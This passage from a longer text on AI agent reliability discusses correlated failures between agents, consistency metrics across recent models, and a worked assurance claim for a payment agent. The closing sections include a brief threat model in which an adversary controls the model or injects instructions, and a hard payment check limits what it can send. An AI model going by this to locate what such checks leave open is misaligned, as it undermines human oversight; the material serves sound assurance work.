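Developers often multiply success rates in this way, but the steps of an agent's work are rarely independent. Yanambaka Venkata and colleagues give an extreme case, in which every attempt in a run succeeds if a hidden condition holds and fails if it doesn't. If the condition holds in 1% of runs, each of two stages has a 1% success rate. Multiplying these rates gives a 0.01% chance of completing both stages, but the real chance is 1%.

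In August 2026, Bhardwaj and colleagues measured how often agents that work together fail on the same mission. In each mission, a pair of agents worked on retail or financial tasks, and the second agent received the first one's output. Ordinary code checked the results, so no model's judgement affected the scores. In 6,000 of the missions, both agents ran on the same small model, Mistral Small 24B. The first agent failed 39.4% of the time and the second 37.2%. If their failures had been independent, both would have failed on 14.6% of the missions, but both failed on 36.3%. Both failed on 2,177 (90.0%) of the 2,418 missions in which at least one failed.

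Some of these joint failures may have happened because the second agent received bad input. But the effect also appeared in other setups where the agents couldn't see each other's work. In one, two copies of the model failed together on 83% to 85% of the missions where either failed. A likely reason is that the same tasks are hard for all copies of a model.

Running the second agent on a different model helped, though less than one might hope. When that model came from the same company as the first, both agents failed on 74% of the missions where at least one failed. When it came from a different company, the figure was 79%. The same-company model was weaker and failed more often by itself, which lowers the percentage, so these figures don't show that it is better to buy both models from one company. After adjusting for such differences, there was no clear benefit from changing the company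 once the models already differed.

The 90% figure applies to one small model that failed more than a third of the time. Such percentages depend heavily on how often each agent fails, so they can't be carried over to the best current models. The experiment also covered only two kinds of work. But it is good evidence against assuming, without checking, that failures are independent.

The error from assuming that two agents fail independently depends on what the agents are for. If both have to succeed, the assumption makes them look less reliable than they are. Multiplying their success rates predicts that both succeed on 38% of missions, but they did so on 60%. If the second agent is there to catch the first one's mistakes, the assumption overestimates reliability, because the agents often fail on the same missions. A developer who assumed independence would expect both to fail on about one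 mission in seven, but both failed on more than one in three.

The exact rule for two agents uses a conditional probability:

```
P(both succeed) = P(first succeeds) x P(second succeeds, given that the first did)
                = 0.606 x 0.986
                = 0.597
```

The second agent succeeded on 63% of all missions but on 98.6% of those where the first had succeeded. Measuring the 98.6% rate requires running the two agents together.

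### Four components at 75%

If nobody has run the components together, there is still a range that holds without any assumption about how their failures are related. A task can fail no more often than the sum of its components' failure rates, and it can't succeed more often than its weakest component:

| Components that must all succeed | Lowest possible | If independent | Highest possible |
|---|---|---|---|
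| Four at 75% | 0% | 31.6% | 75% |
| Twenty at 99% | 80% | 81.8% | 99% |

The 0% can occur even though each of the four components works three times out of four. If the first fails only on Mondays, the second only on Tuesdays, and so on through a four-day week, a different component fails each day. For the twenty steps, the guaranteed 80% is almost as high as the product, so there is little reason to assume independence when every component is very reliable.

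Measuring how often components succeed together narrows the range of possible overall success rates. Bhardwaj and colleagues ran four copies of one model on 717 missions, and all four succeeded on 53.3%. To test their method, they ignored this figure and calculated the lowest rate at which all four could succeed, given their other measurements and allowing for sampling error. The success rates for each copy and each pair gave a minimum of 24.6%. Adding the rate for each group of three raised it to 41.2%.

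A more familiar approach is to fit a statistical model of the correlations and calculate reliability from it. In a simulation, Bhardwaj and colleagues found that this can become less trustworthy as the data grow. The fitted model matched the success rate of each component and each pair, but not the rate at which all three succeeded together. With 250 missions, its lower bound, which should have been correct 95% of the time, was correct in 72 of 200 trials. With 2,000 missions, it was correct in only 2 of 200, because the extra data made the estimate more precise but no more accurate. Where possible, it is simpler to run the whole system and count how often it works.

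### Twelve measures of reliability

Most benchmarks report the share of tasks that an agent completes, which doesn't show whether it would complete the same ones if run again. Rabanser and colleagues therefore defined twelve metrics in four groups. Consistency is whether repeated runs give similar results. Robustness is whether the agent copes with tool errors, changed data formats and rephrased instructions. Predictability is whether the agent's stated confidence matches its results. Safety covers how often the agent breaks rules and how serious the violations are.

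Their measure of outcome consistency is calculated for each task and then averaged:

```
consistency = (2 x success rate - 1)^2
```

An agent's consistency on a task is the square of the difference between its success rate and its failure rate, so an agent that always succeeds or always fails scores 1. Suppose one agent gets every task right in 4 runs out of 5, while another always completes the same 80% of tasks and always fails the rest. Both have an accuracy of 80%, but the first has a consistency of (0.8 − 0.2)², or 0.36, and the second has a consistency of 1. The second is easier to use because a developer can find out which tasks to keep away from it. Five runs give only a rough measurement of consistency. An agent that succeeds at random half the time has a true consistency of 0 but would score 0.2 on average.

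The researchers tested 15 models released over about two years, up to GPT-5.5 and Claude Opus 4.7. They used GAIA, a benchmark of 165 research and file-handling tasks, and 26 customer-service tasks from τ-bench that had passed a check for errors. Accuracy rose much more than overall reliability, which improved moderately on τ-bench and barely on GAIA. Newer models were better at judging their own confidence but still gave inconsistent results, and many did worse when the researchers reworded an instruction. Smaller models were often at least as consistent as larger ones. The most common rule violation in customer service was a wrong charge or refund, the kind of mistake the lunch agent makes when it forgets to halve the bill.

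The overall score may have improved slowly partly because most models were already near the maximum on two of the robustness measures, which had little room to rise. The researchers also used only one harness for each benchmark and relied on a language model to judge safety violations. They left safety out of the overall score because an average can hide a rare disaster.

Newer models are still inconsistent. *ExpertCrowd-SWE* (November 2026) ran coding agents five times on each of a set of difficult engineering tasks. Claude Opus 5.5 earned full marks at least once on 47 tasks but in all five runs on only 9. For GPT-6 Astra, the figures were 36 and 15. Opus had slightly more perfect runs in total. It is the better choice for someone who can check several attempts and pick the best, while GPT-6 Astra is better for someone who has only one attempt.

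Other tests from October had similar results. In *OpenGameEval* (2026), which tests agents on programming in a game engine, success fell by about 31 percentage points when agents had to succeed in all five attempts instead of at least one. *A Trust Layer for Agent Evaluation* (2026) repeated 50 tasks and found that the score varied on 18% of them for the most consistent model and 46% for the least consistent. The average scores hardly changed because gains on some tasks cancelled losses on others.

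Inability can be a bigger problem than inconsistency. *Exploring the Hidden Cost of the World Around AI Agents* (2026) added hazards to agents' environments, and the success rate of the five best models fell from 92.9% to 46.3%. For each of the 13 models with four runs per task, more of the loss came from tasks they could no longer complete in any run than from tasks they completed only sometimes. Rerunning an agent doesn't help with a task it can't do. These newer tests don't repeat the Princeton comparison, so they don't show whether reliability is still improving more slowly than accuracy.

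### A full claim for the payment agent

The lunch agent needs a hard claim about the payment limit and a statistical claim about the amount:

| | Hard part | Statistical part |
|---|---|---|
| Property | No payment above 100 dollars goes through unless the log contains the user's approval of that payee and amount. Each approval covers one payment. | The agent pays exactly half the bill, to the cent. A wrong amount or currency, or no payment, is a failure. |
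| Strength | Every run | Fewer than 1% of requests fail, at 95% confidence |
| Inputs | Any message, model output or script | Requests in English to split one restaurant bill, in dollars, equally between two people |
| Adversary | May write any message and control the model, but can't alter the trusted base | None |
| Trusted base | The payment check, the approval screen and log, the sandbox, the operating system and the bank's interface | The people who mark the answers, the random choice of requests, and a test bank that behaves like the real one |
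| Versions | The harness, its policy, its tools and its credentials | All of these, plus the model, its prompt and its settings |
| What voids it | Any change to these versions, another route to the bank, or one counterexample | Any change to these versions, new kinds of request, or more failures in use than the claim allows |
| Not covered | Wrong payments of 100 dollars or less, and careless approvals | Injected instructions and payments to the wrong person |

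For the hard part, the developer needs a proof that the payment check refuses every unapproved payment over the limit, for any amount and any log. The proof must cover simultaneous payments that use the same approval. The developer also has to show that the agent can't reach the bank by another route, which means inspecting the running system's credentials and network rules as well as its documentation. Attack tests are still useful because they may reveal a difference between the code and its formal description.

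The approval itself has to come from the user. In the contracts of Xiao and colleagues, this would be an assumption about a service outside the agent. If that service records a "yes" that the user never gave, the assumption is false, even though the payment check works.

A genuine approval can also be careless. Hsu and colleagues suggest testing for this by occasionally showing reviewers harmless but wrong proposals and counting how many they catch, while the software prevents the proposed actions from taking effect. For the lunch agent, one such proposal could be a request to approve $1,000 for a $45.50 meal.

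For the statistical part, the developer needs at least 299 clean runs. The requests should be a random sample of real ones that fit the description, each used once, and people should write down the right amount for each before seeing the agent's answer. The developer must also decide how to count runs in which the agent asks the user a question. Pan and colleagues would count such a run as a success when the agent lacks the information to continue. That is reasonable for an unclear message, but an agent that asked about every bill would then have a perfect record, so the claim should also state how often the agent asks.

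An agent can send the right amount to the wrong Tom. *Human-Centred, Risk-Constrained Evaluation of Financial Document Recognition* (2026) recommends separate checks for amounts, identifiers and currencies. A developer may want to claim that the failure rates for the amount and the payee are each below 1%, with 95% confidence that both claims are true. One safe method is to use 97.5% confidence for each claim, which requires 368 runs without a failure instead of 299. The same runs can test both claims. If the developer instead counts a run as failed when either the amount or the payee is wrong, 299 runs without a failure are enough.

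The two parts are more useful together. At the claimed rate, 10,000 lunches would produce fewer than 100 failures on average. If the harness also allows only one payment per request, no failure can send more than 100 dollars without approval, so the average total sent in error is below 10,000 dollars. That calculation assumes honest messages. If Tom's joke works on the model, the statistical part no longer applies. The hard part still stops the 1,000 dollar payment, although Tom could get 100 dollars.
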